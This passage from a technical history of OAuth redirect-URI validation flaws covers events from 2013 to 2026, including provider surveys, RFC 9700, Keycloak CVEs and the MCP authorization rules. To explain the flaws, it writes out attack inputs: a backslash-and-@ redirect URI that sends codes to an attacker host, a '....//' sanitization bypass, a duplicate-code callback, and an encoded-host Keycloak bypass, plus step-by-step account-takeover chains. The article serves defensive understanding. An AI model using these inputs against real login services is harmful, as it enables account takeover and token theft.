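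5. Gist's session cookie contained the victim's access token, encoded but not encrypted. The token covered only gists.
6. The authorization link can also name the permissions it wants, and GitHub approved any request from Gist automatically. By asking for `repo` in the link, Homakov could get a token that read and changed private repositories.

The attack used no scripts, so a browser extension that blocks them would not have stopped it. Either of two standard rules would have stopped it. Exact matching would have made GitHub refuse the address in step 1, and a proper check at the exchange would have made it refuse the code in step 4. Homakov notes that neither bug was much use without the other. Labunets treats the image address in step 3 as the same kind of parsing disagreement as the one over `/../`.

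Homakov received $4,000, which Threatpost's *Five OAuth Bugs Lead to Github Hack* called the program's highest reward so far. GitHub reported that it had tightened the rewriting of image links, set every link in a gist to send no Referer, removed the token from the cookie, revoked tokens that might have leaked, and cut Gist's permissions to public profile information. It also removed third-party login from Speaker Deck, its slide-sharing site, because Homakov had shown that attackers could take over accounts there through an unfixed problem in Facebook's login.

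GitHub's *Open redirect* (2014) credits a researcher called adob with finding similar mistakes in how GitHub parsed redirect addresses, some of which could give an attacker access to OAuth applications as another user. Later, PortSwigger reported that a researcher named Bowling had found another open redirect at GitHub and examined how it affected the tokens of built-in applications such as Gist.

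### Covert Redirect, May 2014

On May 2, 2014, CNET reported a serious flaw in OAuth and OpenID, an older login protocol. Wang Jing, a doctoral student at Nanyang Technological University in Singapore, had named it Covert Redirect and given it a website and a logo. The attacker gives a return address on a client's site that forwards the browser elsewhere, as Goldshlager had done with Skype a year earlier. On the blog tetraph (2014), Wang wrote that the flaw could expose users' tokens and affected most major providers, including Facebook, Google, Microsoft, LinkedIn, PayPal and GitHub. In the GitHub example, the client was travis-ci.com, a software testing site, and a Tumblr page stood in for the attacker's site.

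The press compared Covert Redirect to Heartbleed, a bug in the encryption library OpenSSL that had caused alarm the month before. InternetNews' *Covert Redirect is No Heartbleed* (2014) describes an inbox full of claims about "the next Heartbleed". Symantec rejected the comparison. An attacker could exploit Heartbleed just by sending requests to any unpatched server, while Covert Redirect required finding a vulnerable client and then getting users to cooperate. Coverage that placed the hole in OAuth itself also wrongly suggested that it could be patched in one place.

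In *Security Farce*, Tim Bray (2014), a software developer who knew OAuth well, criticized the coverage as amateurish. He clicked Wang's demonstration links and saw nothing surprising. He was right that the reports gave readers no way to judge the claim, but he also thought the attack would need "weird browser hackery" to read the fragment and a user who pasted an address into their own browser. Poole had shown in 2011 that it needed neither, because Firefox and Chrome carried the fragment over automatically.

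Several specialists replied that the problem was old. Hodges (2014) wrote to a cryptography mailing list, in *"Covert Redirect" vulnerability in OAuth, OpenID*, that a 2012 paper on OpenID had probably covered it. Sakimura, who co-wrote the OpenID Connect standard, said people had known of the attack for at least six years. They were right, and Wang's name for the attack, "Covert Redirect", added little to the term "open redirector".

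They also argued that the standards already prevented it. *Covert Redirect* (2014), a blog post by a developer of OAuth server software, quotes the OpenID Connect rule that a redirect URI must exactly match a registered one. That rule would have stopped the attack on most clients, but it is not part of plain OAuth 2.0, which let the query vary when a client had registered only part of its address. The attack on `/cb?*` only needs to change the query. Sakimura acknowledged this difference and still rated the risk for a compliant OAuth server as low, partly because clients should check `state`. In the implicit grant that check comes too late, because `state` is in the fragment and a redirector on the client's server forwards the browser without receiving it.

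Wang was right about how many providers were exposed, or at least closer than the critics allowed. Many did not follow the strict reading of the standard. *Make Redirection Evil Again* reports that QQ, which was on Wang's list, checked only the domain of the redirect URI until February 2018. Facebook did not dispute the problem. According to Security Affairs' *Covert Redirect security vulnerability found in OAuth and OpenID*, it told Wang that it could not fix this in the short term without forcing every application to use a list of approved addresses. But being on Wang's list did not prove that a provider leaked tokens, because that depended on its matching rule, its support for the implicit grant, and the clients.

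The remaining disagreement was about who should fix the problem. Sakimura blamed clients and told them to remove their open redirectors, adding that servers could help by matching redirect URIs exactly. *Security Considerations*, a guide for developers, points to the OAuth community site's own advisory, number 2014.1, and blames authorization servers that do not require an exact match. The guide's position is more practical, because a provider can protect all its users by changing one comparison, whereas thousands of clients would each have to find every redirector they run. Lodderstedt and colleagues, including John Bradley, one of OAuth's main architects and a critic in 2014, eventually required both exact matching by servers and the removal of open redirectors by clients.

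### Every page on the host

A credential is safe only if no page that the match function accepts for a client passes it on to someone else. Under exact matching, the function accepts just the registered callbacks, and a developer can check the code behind them. If the server compares only the host, the function accepts every page on the site. For Skype that would include a redirector on a statistics server, and for Dropbox a file that a stranger had uploaded.

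The leaking page can pass the credential to the attacker indirectly. According to Homakov, any chain of redirects that starts on a permitted domain and ends on a page with the attacker's script is enough to steal it. LevelBlue's *Third Party Auth Token Theft* warns that any web component that stores or resends data, not only a redirector, can leak a token, as an image did in GitHub's case.

Exact matching does not protect against the first case in Sakimura's analysis, where the registered address is itself an open redirector. The developer then has only one page to fix, but a developer who registers a whole host has to make sure every page on it is safe, including pages that users write. The same is true of anyone who lets a secret proxy send a key to a whole host.

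## 2016 to 2023: tests of how providers check the address

The two sides in the Covert Redirect dispute disagreed about how many providers compared redirect URIs loosely, and neither had a count. Between 2019 and 2023, three research groups tested live services. Some of the providers they tested have since changed their checks, so the results are partly out of date.

### When the server and the browser disagree

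*Make Redirection Evil Again*, a 2019 Black Hat talk by a Hong Kong group led by Xianbo Wang, described a search for redirect URIs in which the provider's server would read one host and the user's browser another. Unlike the attacks of 2013 and 2014, attacks using these URIs would not need a leaking page on the client's site. Bug hunters had already reported single cases, including one in 2016 against a login service called Digits. The group tested 50 providers with a program that sends a server many variants of a redirect URI and infers its matching rule from the replies.

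Suppose a provider makes two checks. The address must begin with `https://app.print.example`, and its host must be `app.print.example`. The host check is there to catch addresses like `https://app.print.example.attacker.example`. The attacker asks for this:

```
https://app.print.example.attacker.example\@app.print.example
```

A web address may include a user name before the host, with an @ between them. An attacker can submit an address that contains their own host, a backslash, an @ and then the permitted host. If the server treats the backslash as an ordinary character, it reads everything between `https://` and the @ as a user name and finds the permitted host after it, so the address passes the server's checks. Most browsers treat a backslash as a slash, so they read the attacker's host as the destination and send the code there.

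Of the 50 providers, 22 used some form of pattern matching, and 11 of those were vulnerable, while none of the other 28 was. An exact comparison doesn't require identifying the host in the address, so an attacker can't exploit a parsing disagreement. The overall vulnerability rate of 22% depends heavily on the sample. Five of the ten Chinese providers were vulnerable, but only one of the 22 providers with a bug bounty program was, perhaps because bounty hunters had already found their easy mistakes.

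The most serious case was a large Chinese login provider that Wang and colleagues do not name. It normally compared redirect URIs exactly, but if the client's developer had also filled in a setting called "secure domain", it checked only the domain. The researchers tested 152 popular sites that used this provider, and 142 were vulnerable. Some of them, such as Baidu, also provided logins for other sites, so one stolen login could open several more accounts.

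Because the flaw was in the provider, it affected many clients at once. An attacker could build a page with hundreds of hidden images, each pointing to an authorization link for a different client. A visitor logged in to the provider would leak a code or token for each of these clients they had already approved, without clicking anything.

One cloud platform's authorization request had no `redirect_uri` parameter. The platform put the return address in `state` and checked only its domain, so the backslash trick worked there too. A developer who looked only for `redirect_uri` would have missed this flaw. An attacker could have used it to obtain a key to everything the victim kept on the platform.

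Wang and colleagues reported the flaws to every vulnerable provider. According to their slides, only one switched to comparing complete strings. The others fixed the specific parsing mistake, and the researchers immediately bypassed some of those fixes. Facebook's first fix in 2013 had failed in the same way. PayPal had switched to comparing complete strings in March 2015, when it required all developers to register full addresses.

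### OAuch and the 100 providers

*OAuch* (Philippaerts, Preuveneers and Joosen, 2022) measured how closely 100 live providers followed OAuth's security rules. The tool, also called OAuch, registers with a provider as an ordinary client and then misbehaves in controlled ways, using 113 tests that each check one rule. The researchers took 75 providers from the 10,000 most popular sites and 25 from the top million. They could not test services that charged money, required special hardware or accepted only citizens of certain countries.

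Only 53% of the providers compared redirect URIs exactly, and 37% did not check the redirect URI when the client exchanged the code. Some providers also lacked other safeguards against stolen codes. Of all the providers, 14% accepted the same code more than once, and 11% of the providers that issued client secrets did not require the secret at the exchange. Popular providers did no better overall than obscure ones.

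Innocenti and colleagues later cited OAuch as showing that only 34% of providers validated the redirect URI correctly. That number seems to come from the OAuch abstract, which says that providers failed to implement 34% of security rules on average. The closest actual finding is that Philippaerts and colleagues rated 35% of code-issuing providers as fully protected against the attack Hardt describes, in which the attacker has the genuine client redeem a stolen code. Full protection requires both exact matching and a working check when the code is exchanged.

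A provider could fail OAuch's exact-matching test without breaking a firm rule of the 2012 OAuth standard. When several documents covered the same point, the researchers applied the strictest, which here was a draft of the IETF's later security advice. Most operators had not known that anything was missing. Some told the researchers that they did not follow the draft because it was not an official standard, while others did not want to break existing clients or thought that clients should defend themselves.

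CyberArk's *How Secure Is Your OAuth?*, an undated survey by a security company, gives a lower figure. It found that 28 of 100 websites did not verify the redirect URI properly, and that 18 of those accepted any path after the domain. The samples and tests differ too much for the two surveys to show a trend.

### Twenty altered paths

Innocenti and colleagues tested fewer providers but carried the attack further, through to an account takeover. They began with a February 2022 list of the 15,000 most popular websites, and their software found 728 with a login page that offered at least one outside provider. They kept the 28 providers that three or more sites used, then dropped those that demanded real personal details, restricted users by country or required two-factor login. The sample shrank again because some sites blocked automated logins. They ended with 16 providers, 378 client sites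 and 464 completed OAuth flows.

For each flow, a program logged in through Chrome with a test account. A proxy intercepted the authorization request and altered the redirect URI, and the researchers repeated this with 20 alterations. The simplest added `/FAKEPATH` to the genuine callback address. Others used `..` to move up out of the callback's path, or disguised the dots and slashes by encoding them once or twice. A provider failed if it sent the browser to an address that still contained `FAKEPATH`.

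Six of the 16 providers failed: Atlassian, Facebook, GitHub, Microsoft, the South Korean web portal NAVER, and VK. They let the attacker choose a different page on the client's site, but not a different host.

### A second code in the reply

The other experiment left the path alone and changed the query. The researchers registered their own client with all 16 providers and requested a redirect URI that already contained a code, such as `https://print.example/callback?code=ATTACKER`. A provider that accepts this address adds the real code when it replies, and the browser arrives at the client with two:

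```
GET /callback?code=ATTACKER&code=Xw93bTqL&state=k7Qz
Host: print.example
```

Ten of the 16 providers delivered both the attacker's code and the victim's to the client. OAuth does not specify which one the client should use, so some programs take the first and some take the last. If the client takes the attacker's code, the victim's remains unused.

| Accepted an altered path | Delivered two codes | Providers |
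|---|---|---|
| Yes | Yes | GitHub, Microsoft, NAVER, VK |
| Yes | No | Atlassian, Facebook |
| No | Yes | LINE, LinkedIn, OK, ORCID, Slack, Yahoo |
| No | No | Dropbox, Kakao, Twitter, Yandex |

Innocenti and colleagues then tested whether providers check the redirect URI when a client exchanges the code for a token. Their client started a flow with an altered redirect URI and sent the original one with the code. A correct server refuses because the two differ. GitHub and NAVER issued a token anyway, and also did so when the client omitted the redirect URI. GitHub's documentation listed the parameter as optional. In 2014, Homakov had exploited the same two weaknesses at GitHub, which accepted an altered path and did not check the redirect URI at the exchange.

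The 14 providers that passed could still be unsafe with some clients. Some clients allow extra parameters in their callback address and rebuild the redirect URI for the exchange from whatever parameters arrived. Such a client copies the attacker's code into the rebuilt address, making it identical to the address in the doctored request. The researchers simulated this with the ten providers that delivered two codes, and six completed the exchange: GitHub, LinkedIn, NAVER, OK, Slack and VK.

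### Why an unused code is worth stealing

An attacker who steals a code from the genuine callback page has to use it before the client does. Both techniques remove that race because the client never redeems the real code, which works until it expires. An altered path sends the browser to a page that isn't built to handle codes, and a duplicate code parameter leads the client to redeem the wrong code.

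This makes small leaks useful to attackers. In 46 of the 464 flows, Innocenti and colleagues found that the callback page sent OAuth values to other companies' servers. The leaks involved 30 client sites, 11 providers and 76 receiving domains. Ad networks were the largest group of recipients. Many ad networks sell space by real-time bidding, sending each advertiser details of the visit while the page loads. Those details can include the page's address, and therefore the code. Anyone can sign up as an advertiser, so an attacker could receive codes this way.

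Normally the client has already used the code by the time a bidder reads it. But an attacker can put a false code into the redirect URI so that the client's login fails, and then collect the real one from the bid request. If the provider also fails to check the redirect URI when exchanging the code for a token, the attacker can take over the account. The researchers confirmed that this worked with real websites.

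If the provider also accepts an altered path, the attacker can use leaks anywhere on the client's site, such as an ad on another page, a page where visitors can insert their own HTML, or another customer's section of a shared site.

### The attack through NAVER

To test the whole chain on a real site, Innocenti and colleagues did not look for a new flaw. They searched Open Bug Bounty, a public register of website vulnerabilities, for sites in their sample with known open redirectors that nobody had fixed. They picked one from 2018 that its reporter had rated a very low risk. The site, which they do not name, let people log in with NAVER. The attack went as follows:

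1. The attacker writes a link to NAVER's real login page. The redirect URI in it begins with the site's registered callback, climbs back up with disguised `..` steps, and ends at the redirector, with the attacker's server as the place to forward to.
2. The victim opens the link and logs in on NAVER's own page.
3. NAVER accepts the redirect URI and sends the browser there with a code. The steps lead to the redirector instead of the callback.
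4. The redirector forwards the browser to the attacker's server, and the code goes with it. (The redirector must have passed it on, or the Referer header did.)
5. The attacker starts an ordinary login on the site, stops it just before the browser returns from NAVER, and replaces their own code with the victim's.
6. The site redeems the code with its own secret. NAVER does not compare the redirect URIs, so it issues a token, and the attacker is logged in as the victim.

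The attack worked only if NAVER failed at steps 3 and 6 and the site failed at step 4. Exact matching would have stopped it at step 3, whatever the site did.

### The limits of testing from outside

All three groups could see what a provider did with a request but not the code behind it. The Cerberus researchers read code and could find the faulty line in ApiFest, but they were limited to server libraries because big providers' own software is mostly private.

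When Innocenti and colleagues simulated the client that copies the attacker's code, four providers refused the exchange even though the two addresses were identical. A plain string comparison would have accepted them, so these providers must use some other check. It stopped this attack, but nobody outside the companies knows what it is or what it would let through.

A provider's test result may also depend on how its clients are configured. At the Chinese login provider, one setting decided whether a site was vulnerable. Facebook had offered exact matching since December 2017 and later made it the default, yet it was among the six providers that accepted altered paths. The published results list only providers, so they do not show whether the affected sites had turned exact matching off.

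Passing is weaker evidence than failing, because a provider that refused all 20 altered paths may still accept another. Failing does not mean that attackers can take over accounts, because they still need a client that leaks the code or token and, for a confidential client, a way past the code exchange. Innocenti and colleagues showed complete attacks in two case studies and did not estimate how many sites were exposed.

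### The dispute over the 2012 text

Innocenti and colleagues argue that the flaws come from the standard itself, and that a provider could follow it perfectly and still be vulnerable. Hardt requires "simple string comparison", which checks two strings character by character. The comparison stops when one string ends before the other, but the definition does not state whether that counts as a match. They read this as allowing a server to accept `https://print.example/callback/forum/9` when the client had registered `https://print.example/callback`, because every pair of characters matches until the shorter string ends.

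That reading is hard to accept, because the definition describes a test for equality and two strings of different lengths are not equal. The OpenID Foundation's *OpenID Connect Registration 1.0* repeats OpenID Connect's exact-match rule and cites the same definition for how to compare addresses. In the OpenID Foundation's *Certification* (2023), a discussion that followed one of Innocenti's talks, the person proposing new tests called the standards "quite clear". Hardt is even clearer about the exchange, requiring the two addresses to be "identical".

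The researchers' argument is stronger when the client has registered only part of its address, because the query may then vary, including by an extra `code` parameter. Hardt tells the server to keep the existing query when it adds its own parameters, and elsewhere forbids a response to contain any parameter twice. If the address already contains a `code`, the server can obey both rules only by refusing the request, but Hardt never says so.

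Both forms of registration that Hardt recommends include the path, so the six providers that accepted altered paths were looser than the 2012 text advises, however one reads the definition of string comparison.

Still, the rule was easy to miss. Wang and colleagues quote a passage from the standard's security chapter that requires servers to "validate" the redirect URI, and they point out that it does not explain how. The explanation is in a different chapter. In the OpenID Foundation's *FAPI2*, a discussion about a stricter version of OAuth for high-risk uses such as banking, one member was not sure that OAuth was explicit enough. Another replied that being more explicit never hurts and that the OAuth 2.1 draft had already moved the rule to a more prominent place.

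The experiments cannot show whether a provider misread an unclear rule or ignored a clear one, because both look the same from outside. There is some evidence that some providers chose deliberately. GitHub had documented its subdirectory rule for years, and the person who made the proposal in the OpenID discussion had overheard that one service let customers add an identifier to the path because the alternative was to register thousands of addresses. Better wording would have helped the operators who told Philippaerts and colleagues that they had not known, but not GitHub or that service.

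### What the providers fixed

Innocenti and colleagues notified all 16 providers and gave them more than 90 days. When the paper came out in December 2023, only Microsoft had confirmed a fix. In later slides, the researchers report that NAVER had also fixed the problem and paid them a bounty, and that GitHub was working on a fix. The other affected providers acknowledged the report but gave no information about repairs. The table above describes the services at the time of the study, and at least two entries are out of date. The findings also led the IETF to clarify its draft advice and the OpenID Foundation to change its conformance tests.

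### Validating without sanitizing

The paper ends with three recommendations, which apply both when the authorization request arrives and when the client exchanges the code.

The two addresses should match byte for byte. This blocks all 20 altered paths, and also the duplicate code, unless the client has registered an address that contains one.

The server should refuse any request whose redirect URI contains one of OAuth's own parameter names, such as `code` or `state`. This matters most for servers that still let the query string vary.

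The server should never sanitize a redirect URI. To sanitize a value is to repair it, for instance by removing suspicious characters or decoding encoded ones, and then carry on. To validate it is to accept or refuse it as it stands. Suppose a server deletes every `../` it finds, to stop attackers climbing out of the callback path. An attacker sends this:

```
https://app.print.example/callback/....//forum/9
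```

The server removes one `../` from the middle of the dots and slashes. The remaining characters join to form a new `../`, so the cleaned address leads to the forum. The attacker's original address did not move up a directory, so the server's cleaning created the attack. More careful cleaning can prevent this particular trick, but each transformation still leaves two versions of the address, and the server may check one while the browser follows the other. A server has to decode the link's parameter to read the address, but it should not change the address after that.

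The 2012 standard does give bad advice here. Innocenti and colleagues quote a passage that requires servers and clients to sanitize the values they receive, and to validate them "when possible". The passage names `redirect_uri` as one of the most important values. Innocenti and colleagues recommend the reverse order, with validation first.

They expect strict comparison to break some clients, such as those that reorder query parameters at the exchange or sit behind a proxy that rewrites requests. For these clients, they suggest a less secure mode that the client's developers must switch on themselves. The Chinese login provider's "secure domain" setting was similar. The provider also offered exact matching, but 142 of the 152 sites that Wang and colleagues tested used the looser check.

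## 2017 to 2026: exact matching becomes the rule

The IETF's OAuth working group took almost eight years to go from proposing exact matching to requiring it. *Security Topics* (Lodderstedt, 2016), a draft the group had not yet adopted, had already listed exact matching as the countermeasure to loose checks. The group's own first draft, *OAuth Security Topics* (Lodderstedt, Bradley and Labunets, 2017), proposed it in March 2017.

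The three authors blamed the flaws on the complexity of pattern matching, so instead of designing a better matcher, they proposed dropping patterns and having the server compare two strings. The IETF published the final text in January 2025 as RFC 9700. In it, Lodderstedt and colleagues give the same reason, writing that patterns proved "more complex to implement and more error-prone to manage" than exact matching.

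The 2017 draft also lists the drawbacks of the change. Clients would have to keep their transaction data in the `state` parameter instead of varying the query, as the 2012 standard allowed. The number of clients that relied on varying the query was unknown, and the draft includes a request for the group to collect data. Clients with several callback addresses would have to register each one, and some native apps (apps installed on a device) would stop working.

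Exact matching also rules out putting a one-time secret in the redirect URI, because a client can't register an address that changes with every login. Such a secret could let the check at the code exchange detect a code stolen from another copy of the same client, since the two secrets would differ. PKCE now provides this protection, and RFC 9700 requires it for public clients and recommends it for confidential ones.

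The wording became firmer with each draft. In November 2017, *Security Topics* (Lodderstedt, 2017) listed "shall utilize exact matching" among measures for the group to consider. By version 13, the verb was "MUST" and the list contained the group's own recommendations. Version 21 specified "exact string matching", with an exception for port numbers. The final text reads "authorization servers MUST utilize exact string matching", and a later passage requires the server to ensure that the two addresses are equal. This rules out the reading that Innocenti and colleagues had found in the 2012 standard, under which a longer address could match a shorter one.

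RFC 9700 is a Best Current Practice, which represents the consensus of the IETF, whereas the 2013 advice was only informational. Some operators had told Philippaerts and colleagues that they ignored the draft because it was not official, but that reason no longer applies since RFC 9700 was published in January 2025. The IETF still cannot force anyone to comply. Lodderstedt and colleagues concede that some existing systems are incompatible with the new rules and that following them may break connections between systems, but they recommend upgrading "as soon as feasible".

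### The port exception for native apps

A desktop app usually has no public web server to receive a redirect, so it can open a small server on the user's machine, at the loopback address 127.0.0.1 or the name `localhost`, which only programs on that machine can reach. The operating system often gives the app whichever port is free, so the developer can't register it in advance.

RFC 9700 therefore requires authorization servers to accept any port in these addresses. If an app has registered `http://127.0.0.1/callback`, the server accepts `http://127.0.0.1:51004/callback` and `http://127.0.0.1:62310/callback`. It refuses `http://127.0.0.1:51004/other`, because everything except the port must still match.

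The exception is safe against a remote attacker because the browser delivers the code to the user's own machine whatever the port. For the same reason, the address may use unencrypted HTTP, which RFC 9700 forbids for other redirect URIs.

However, a malicious program on the same machine can also open a port. The 2017 draft concluded that, for native apps, checking the redirect URI prevents impersonation only if the app uses an HTTPS address that it has claimed as its own.

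### The exception for pushed requests

In a pushed authorization request, the client sends the request directly to the authorization server instead of putting it in the browser link. The printing service's server would send its `redirect_uri`, `state` and other parameters together with its client secret. The authorization server stores them and returns a reference, and the browser link then contains little else (the values are invented):

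```
GET /authorize?client_id=print-shop-41
    &request_uri=urn%3Aietf%3Aparams%3Aoauth
     %3Arequest_uri%3A6esc11
Host: login.photos.example
```

Unlike the similarly named `redirect_uri`, `request_uri` is only a reference to the stored request, so this link contains no redirect URI for an attacker to change.

RFC 9126, the standard for pushed authorization requests, lets a server accept unregistered redirect URIs from an authenticated client. One participant in the OpenID Foundation's *FAPI2* discussion justified this on the grounds that an attacker can't set an arbitrary value in a request that doesn't pass through the browser. Lodderstedt and colleagues state more generally that a server may trust the redirect URI without further checks if it can verify who sent the request and that nobody altered it. OAuth 1.0a had relied on the same idea since 2009, when it moved the callback into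 the client's first, signed request.

The exception depends on client authentication, because a public client has no secret and anyone could push a request in its name. An attacker who steals a confidential client's secret could still push a request with their own redirect URI, which a list of registered URIs would have prevented.

Because of this exception, the group working on FAPI 2, the stricter OAuth for banking, closed a proposal to require exact matching without adopting it. One participant thought the requirement made sense if FAPI 2 did not need unregistered addresses. But FAPI 2 requires pushed requests, and the formal analysis of its security had already assumed that clients could use any address.

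### Tests, libraries and OAuth 2.1

The OpenID Foundation certifies login servers with automated tests. Until 2023, one test registered a callback and then requested a different page beside it. In the example that the OpenID Foundation discussed, the paths were these:

| Use | Path |
|---|---|
| Registered | `/test/a/JustPassMe/callback` |
| Old test, which the server must refuse | `/test/a/JustPassMe/39Y8nOAX3K` |
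| Proposed test, which the server must refuse | `/test/a/JustPassMe/callback/39Y8nOAX3K` |

After a talk by Innocenti, a participant suggested changing the test address, and the working group supported the change on a call on October 2, 2023. A server that matches by prefix passed the old test because it refuses the old address, which does not begin with the registered path. The same server accepts the proposed address, which does begin with that path, and so fails the test. The proposed address alone would not expose a server that mishandles only encoded `..` steps, which were among the alterations that Innocenti and colleagues tried.

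The participant proposed no test for the duplicate `code` parameter. Such a test would have to register a redirect URI that already contained a code, and no specification clearly defined how a server should handle one. The OAuth 2.1 draft, by Hardt and colleagues, now forbids redirect URIs from containing any parameter that OAuth uses in its replies.

Connect2id's *OAuth 2.0 redirect URI validation* describes checks that the company's OAuth software kit runs when it reads an authorization request or a client's registration data. Since version 10.14 the kit has rejected redirect URIs that contain a fragment, or a `code`, `state` or `response` parameter. It also rejects URIs that start with `javascript`, `data` or `vbscript`, which an attacker could use to run code in the browser. Developers still need to compare the redirect URI with the registered one, and Connect2id tells them to use strict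 string matching.

OAuth 2.1 would make exact matching part of the main standard. Version 17 of the draft, from October 2026, requires clients to register their complete redirect URIs, including the path. The 2012 standard allowed partial registration. The server must reject any address that doesn't exactly match a registered one, except that the port may differ on a loopback address. Hardt and colleagues apply this rule to pushed requests by treating the push as a registration made at the time of the request.

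The draft expires on May 4, 2027, because IETF drafts last at most six months. The working group is scheduled to submit the text in December 2026 to the body that approves IETF standards, so final publication is unlikely before 2027. Old clients may keep their old rules for some time after that. Hardt and colleagues let one server support both OAuth 2.0 and OAuth 2.1 and move its clients to the new version one at a time, but they define no signal to show which version a client uses.

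### What exact matching costs developers

Developers who use Keycloak, an open-source login server, have complained about the rule for years. Many teams deploy a temporary preview copy of their site, at a newly generated address, for each proposed change. Keycloak allows a wildcard only at the end of a redirect URI, so the wildcard can't cover a changing host name. Lyck (2021), in *Valid Redirect URIs for dynamic URLs*, called this "a blocker". Thomas Darimont replied that the limit was deliberate, because the OAuth specification recommends explicit addresses.

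In another thread, *OIDC valid redirect URI with wildcard host on port :8006*, an administrator had about 20 servers with changing names and did not want to list each one. Someone replied that security "is not about convenience for administrators", and that OAuth 2.1 would disallow wildcards anyway.

Applications usually handle exact matching with one fixed callback and the `state` parameter. Schmitz von Hülst (2024), in *How to handle redirect_uri with exact string matching in 24.0.3?*, asked whether every page needed its own registered redirect URI to return users to where they were when their session expired, such as `/account/me`. It doesn't, because the application can look up the page from the `state` value when the user returns.

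Preview deployments take more work, because the user has to end up on a different host. Suppose the printing service has a preview copy at `pr-418.preview.print.example`. A login could go like this:

1. The preview copy sends the browser to `https://login.print.example/start`, with its own name in the link.
2. The login host stores that name under a random `state` value and sends the user to the authorization server. The redirect URI is always `https://login.print.example/cb`.
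3. The authorization server finds an exact match and returns the code there.
4. The login host exchanges the code, looks up the `state` value, and sends the browser back to the preview copy with a one-time login code of its own.

In step 4 the login host sends a credential to an address that someone else supplied, so it has to check that address too. If it forwards the login code to any address it is given, an attacker can take over the account even though the authorization server matched the redirect URI exactly. Unlike the authorization server, the printing service has a current list of its preview copies, so the login host can check the name against that list instead of a pattern.

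A 2026 flaw in Ech0, a self-hosted publishing program, shows how this second check can fail. According to Vulners' *Ech0's OAuth redirect URI validation ignores path component, enables exchange-code theft*, Ech0 checked the address that would receive its own exchange code against the administrator's list, but compared only the scheme and host. An attacker could therefore pick a leaking page on a permitted host, as Goldshlager had in 2013 at Skype and Dropbox.

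Other organizations keep wildcards and try to limit the damage. British Columbia's government login service allows them in development and test environments, which is reasonable if the test system holds no real accounts. Okta, a commercial login provider, allows them only if the developer switches them on for an application. Each pattern may contain only one star, as in `https://redirect-*-domain.example.com/oidc/redirect`, and the star can't match across a dot. These limits prevent the worst parsing errors, but an attacker who takes over a host that fits the pattern can still collect codes.

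Ping Identity allows wildcards in the redirect URI path. Its documentation gives the example `https://www.example.com/th*/callback`, which accepts `/this/callback` and `/that/callback` but not `/oidc/callback`. The company recommends exact matching and describes the wildcard as an option for customers who need flexibility. Bradley, who co-wrote the 2017 draft, worked there at the time.

### Keycloak's wildcards

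Keycloak still supports wildcards, and researchers have repeatedly found ways around its checks. Each flaw is listed in CVE, a public register of software vulnerabilities.

GitLab's *CVE-2023-6291* (2024) explains the first. Keycloak decoded a redirect URI before checking it, and the result no longer meant the same as the original. An attacker could submit this, after the `https://`:

```
www%2ekeycloak%2eorg%2fapp%2f:y@example.com
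```

Keycloak decoded `%2e` to a dot and `%2f` to a slash, so it read `www.keycloak.org/app/` and took keycloak.org as the host. The browser used the original text, which has no slash before the @, so it treated everything before the @ as a user name and password and went to example.com. Red Hat, which sells a supported version of Keycloak, warns in *CVE-2023-6291* that an attacker could steal an access token this way and impersonate the victim. Keycloak fixed the flaw, but Red Hat's *CVE-2024-2419* reports another, "very similar" way past the host check.

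INCIBE's *CVE-2023-6927* (2023), an entry in the database of Spain's cybersecurity institute, describes a bypass of the fix for another flaw, CVE-2023-6134. An attacker could use a less common way of delivering the authorization response to steal codes or tokens from clients with a wildcard in their redirect URIs. Tenable's *CVE-2024-1132* describes a separate validation flaw that affected every client that used a wildcard.

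In version 24.0.3, from 2024, Keycloak began requiring an exact match, rather than a wildcard match, for any redirect URI that contains a user name part or a step up to a parent directory. The change covered only those two cases, according to a reply to Schmitz von Hülst, who had thought it abolished wildcards altogether. The person who replied agreed that the documentation was confusing.

This approach works only if Keycloak recognizes every suspicious address, and two flaws published in 2026 show that it did not:

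- OSV's *CVE-2026-3872* (2026), an April entry in an open vulnerability database, describes a bypass that used `..;/`. Some web servers ignore what follows a semicolon in a path segment and treat this as `../`, but a check that looks only for `../` misses it. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-3872* adds that the attacker needs control of another path on the same web server, as a customer on shared hosting might have.
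- Red Hat's *CVE-2026-7504*, which INCIBE's *CVE-2026-7504* (2026) dates to May 19, describes an address with several @ signs. Java's address parser could not extract a user name from it. Keycloak therefore found no user name, fell back to the wildcard comparison, and accepted the address.

The second flaw also has a simpler cause. When the parser failed, Keycloak continued with the looser check instead of refusing the address. For both flaws, Red Hat advises avoiding wildcards and listing the permitted addresses. Four of the six flaws here affect only clients that use a wildcard, so following this advice protects against those four without a patch.

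Keycloak has since narrowed what a wildcard can match. According to its upgrade guide, `https://example.com*` used to accept `https://example.com.other.domain.com`, the same missing-boundary error that OAuth developers were making more than a decade earlier. From version 26.6.3, Keycloak treats that pattern as `https://example.com/*`. It still accepts `https://*`, which allows every HTTPS address, on the grounds that nobody could misunderstand it. The guide recommends against using wildcards.

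### Authorization servers for the Model Context Protocol

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data. An MCP server offers the tools, and the AI application is the client. MCP uses OAuth for authorization, so many developers who had never built an authorization server have had to build or install one.

The March 2025 Model Context Protocol specification (2025) required servers to "validate redirect URIs." Wang and colleagues had criticized the 2012 OAuth standard for using the word "validate" without explaining it.

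A few weeks later, Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, fixed a flaw in `workers-oauth-provider`, a library for building MCP servers. OSV's *GHSA-4pc9-x2fx-p7vj* (2025), the advisory for CVE-2025-4143, reports that the library checked the redirect URI when the client exchanged the code, but not when the authorization request arrived. The check at the exchange is too late because the attacker already has the code.

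An attack also required that the victim had approved the client before and that the application built on the library approved repeat requests automatically. According to the advisory, many applications do. The attacker then only had to get the victim to visit a malicious page. Version 0.0.5 added the missing check.

According to the advisory, the library's author had thought a lot about the requirement during the design and "knew what he was doing but flubbed it", so clearer standards would not have prevented this mistake. An automated test that tried one unregistered redirect URI would have caught it.

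The current specification, dated July 28, 2026, is much more specific. Model Context Protocol (2026) requires authorization servers to implement OAuth 2.1, even though that is still a draft. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) sets these rules for redirects:

- Clients must register their redirect URIs, and the server must compare each request exactly with the registered values.
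- Every redirect URI must use HTTPS or point to `localhost`.
- The server should redirect the browser automatically only if it trusts the address. Otherwise it may tell the user and leave the decision to them.
- Clients must use PKCE and must stop if the server does not advertise support for it.
- Clients should send a `state` value and discard replies that do not return it.

Registration is harder for MCP than for a "Sign in with" button, because a user may connect an AI application to a server that the application's developers have never heard of. Lodderstedt had raised this problem in 2013. MCP now recommends client ID metadata documents. The client publishes a file at a web address, uses that address as its identifier, and lists its redirect URIs in the file. When an authorization server first receives a request from the client, it fetches the file and compares the requested redirect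 URI with the list.

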